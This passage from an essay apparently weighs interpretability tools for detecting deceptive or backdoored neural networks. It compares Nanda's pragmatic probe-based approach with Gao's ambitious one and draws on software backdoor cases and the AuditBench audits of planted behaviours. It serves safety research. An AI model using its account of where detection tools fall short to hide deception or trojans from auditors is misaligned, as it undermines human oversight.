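The idea is a long way off for neural networks. Another reader estimated that existing explanations account for only 20% to 50% of the tiny parts of a model they cover. Nanda added that even the "understood" part might not be safe, because a feature may not mean quite what its label suggests and its exact values could carry extra information.

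The software cases show this second problem. A complete list helps only if a person or program judges its entries correctly. The intruder who weakened Juniper's random number generator changed only constants, so a complete list of the program's functions would have looked the same before and after. A reviewer can also misjudge the right entry, as Claude Opus 4.6 did when it judged the backdoored function in dnsmasq to be legitimate.

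Another of Nanda's readers argued that nobody needs the full list, because if each generation of models helps to train the next, researchers may only need to know whether deception is rising or falling. This might work for a model with a general tendency to deceive, but it wouldn't help with most trojans, such as one that makes a network misread a stop sign with a sticker on it, because they don't involve such a tendency.

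### The turn towards simpler tools

*Against Almost Every Theory of Impact of Interpretability*, a critique that predates this exchange, argued that most goals of interpretability were easier to reach without it, especially the goal of countering deceptive models.

Nanda has not gone that far, but he has come to favour simpler tools. In an interview recorded in July 2025, he told 80,000 Hours that he had become "a big convert to probes", which he called simple and boring but effective. He still doubted that they would be highly reliable, and told a reader of his post that he would be shocked if they exceeded 99% confidence in unfamiliar situations with new generations of models.

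By December his team had moved away from trying to reverse engineer whole networks. *A Pragmatic Vision for Interpretability* describes how the team now chooses problems that matter for safety and measures its progress on test tasks. In a talk that month, *Our Pivot To Pragmatic Interpretability*, Nanda (2025) cited Anthropic's work on whether a Claude model could tell that it was being tested, in which simple changes to the model's activations had been more effective than complex methods.

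In *An Ambitious Vision for Interpretability*, Leo Gao defended the older ambition of finding simple and faithful explanations of how networks work. He argued that researchers were making progress towards this goal, and that such explanations make it much easier to find out what a network is really doing.

The software record supports using Nanda's approach to raise alerts and Gao's to confirm them. Freund did not need to understand xz to see that sshd was using too much processor time, but researchers had to reverse-engineer the backdoor to learn what it was for.

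*Scalable End-to-End Interpretability* takes a position between the two. It agrees with the pragmatists that research should start from real behaviour and data, but argues that both sides miss something important. *The Pragmatic Interpretability Trap* is more critical of the pragmatic approach. One of its objections is that researchers who keep only the tools that beat output-only methods on a test will select for good scores rather than understanding.

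In AuditBench, most tools that read or altered activations would have failed such a test. But one of Nanda's readers argued that studies like this may favour output-only methods. Researchers who plant a behaviour put relatively little effort into how the model talks, while AI companies train their products extensively to sound like friendly assistants. A commercial model's answers may therefore reveal less than a test model's, and its internals may be a better guide. Nanda agreed in principle, and said he had tried to suggest output-only methods that could work despite such training.
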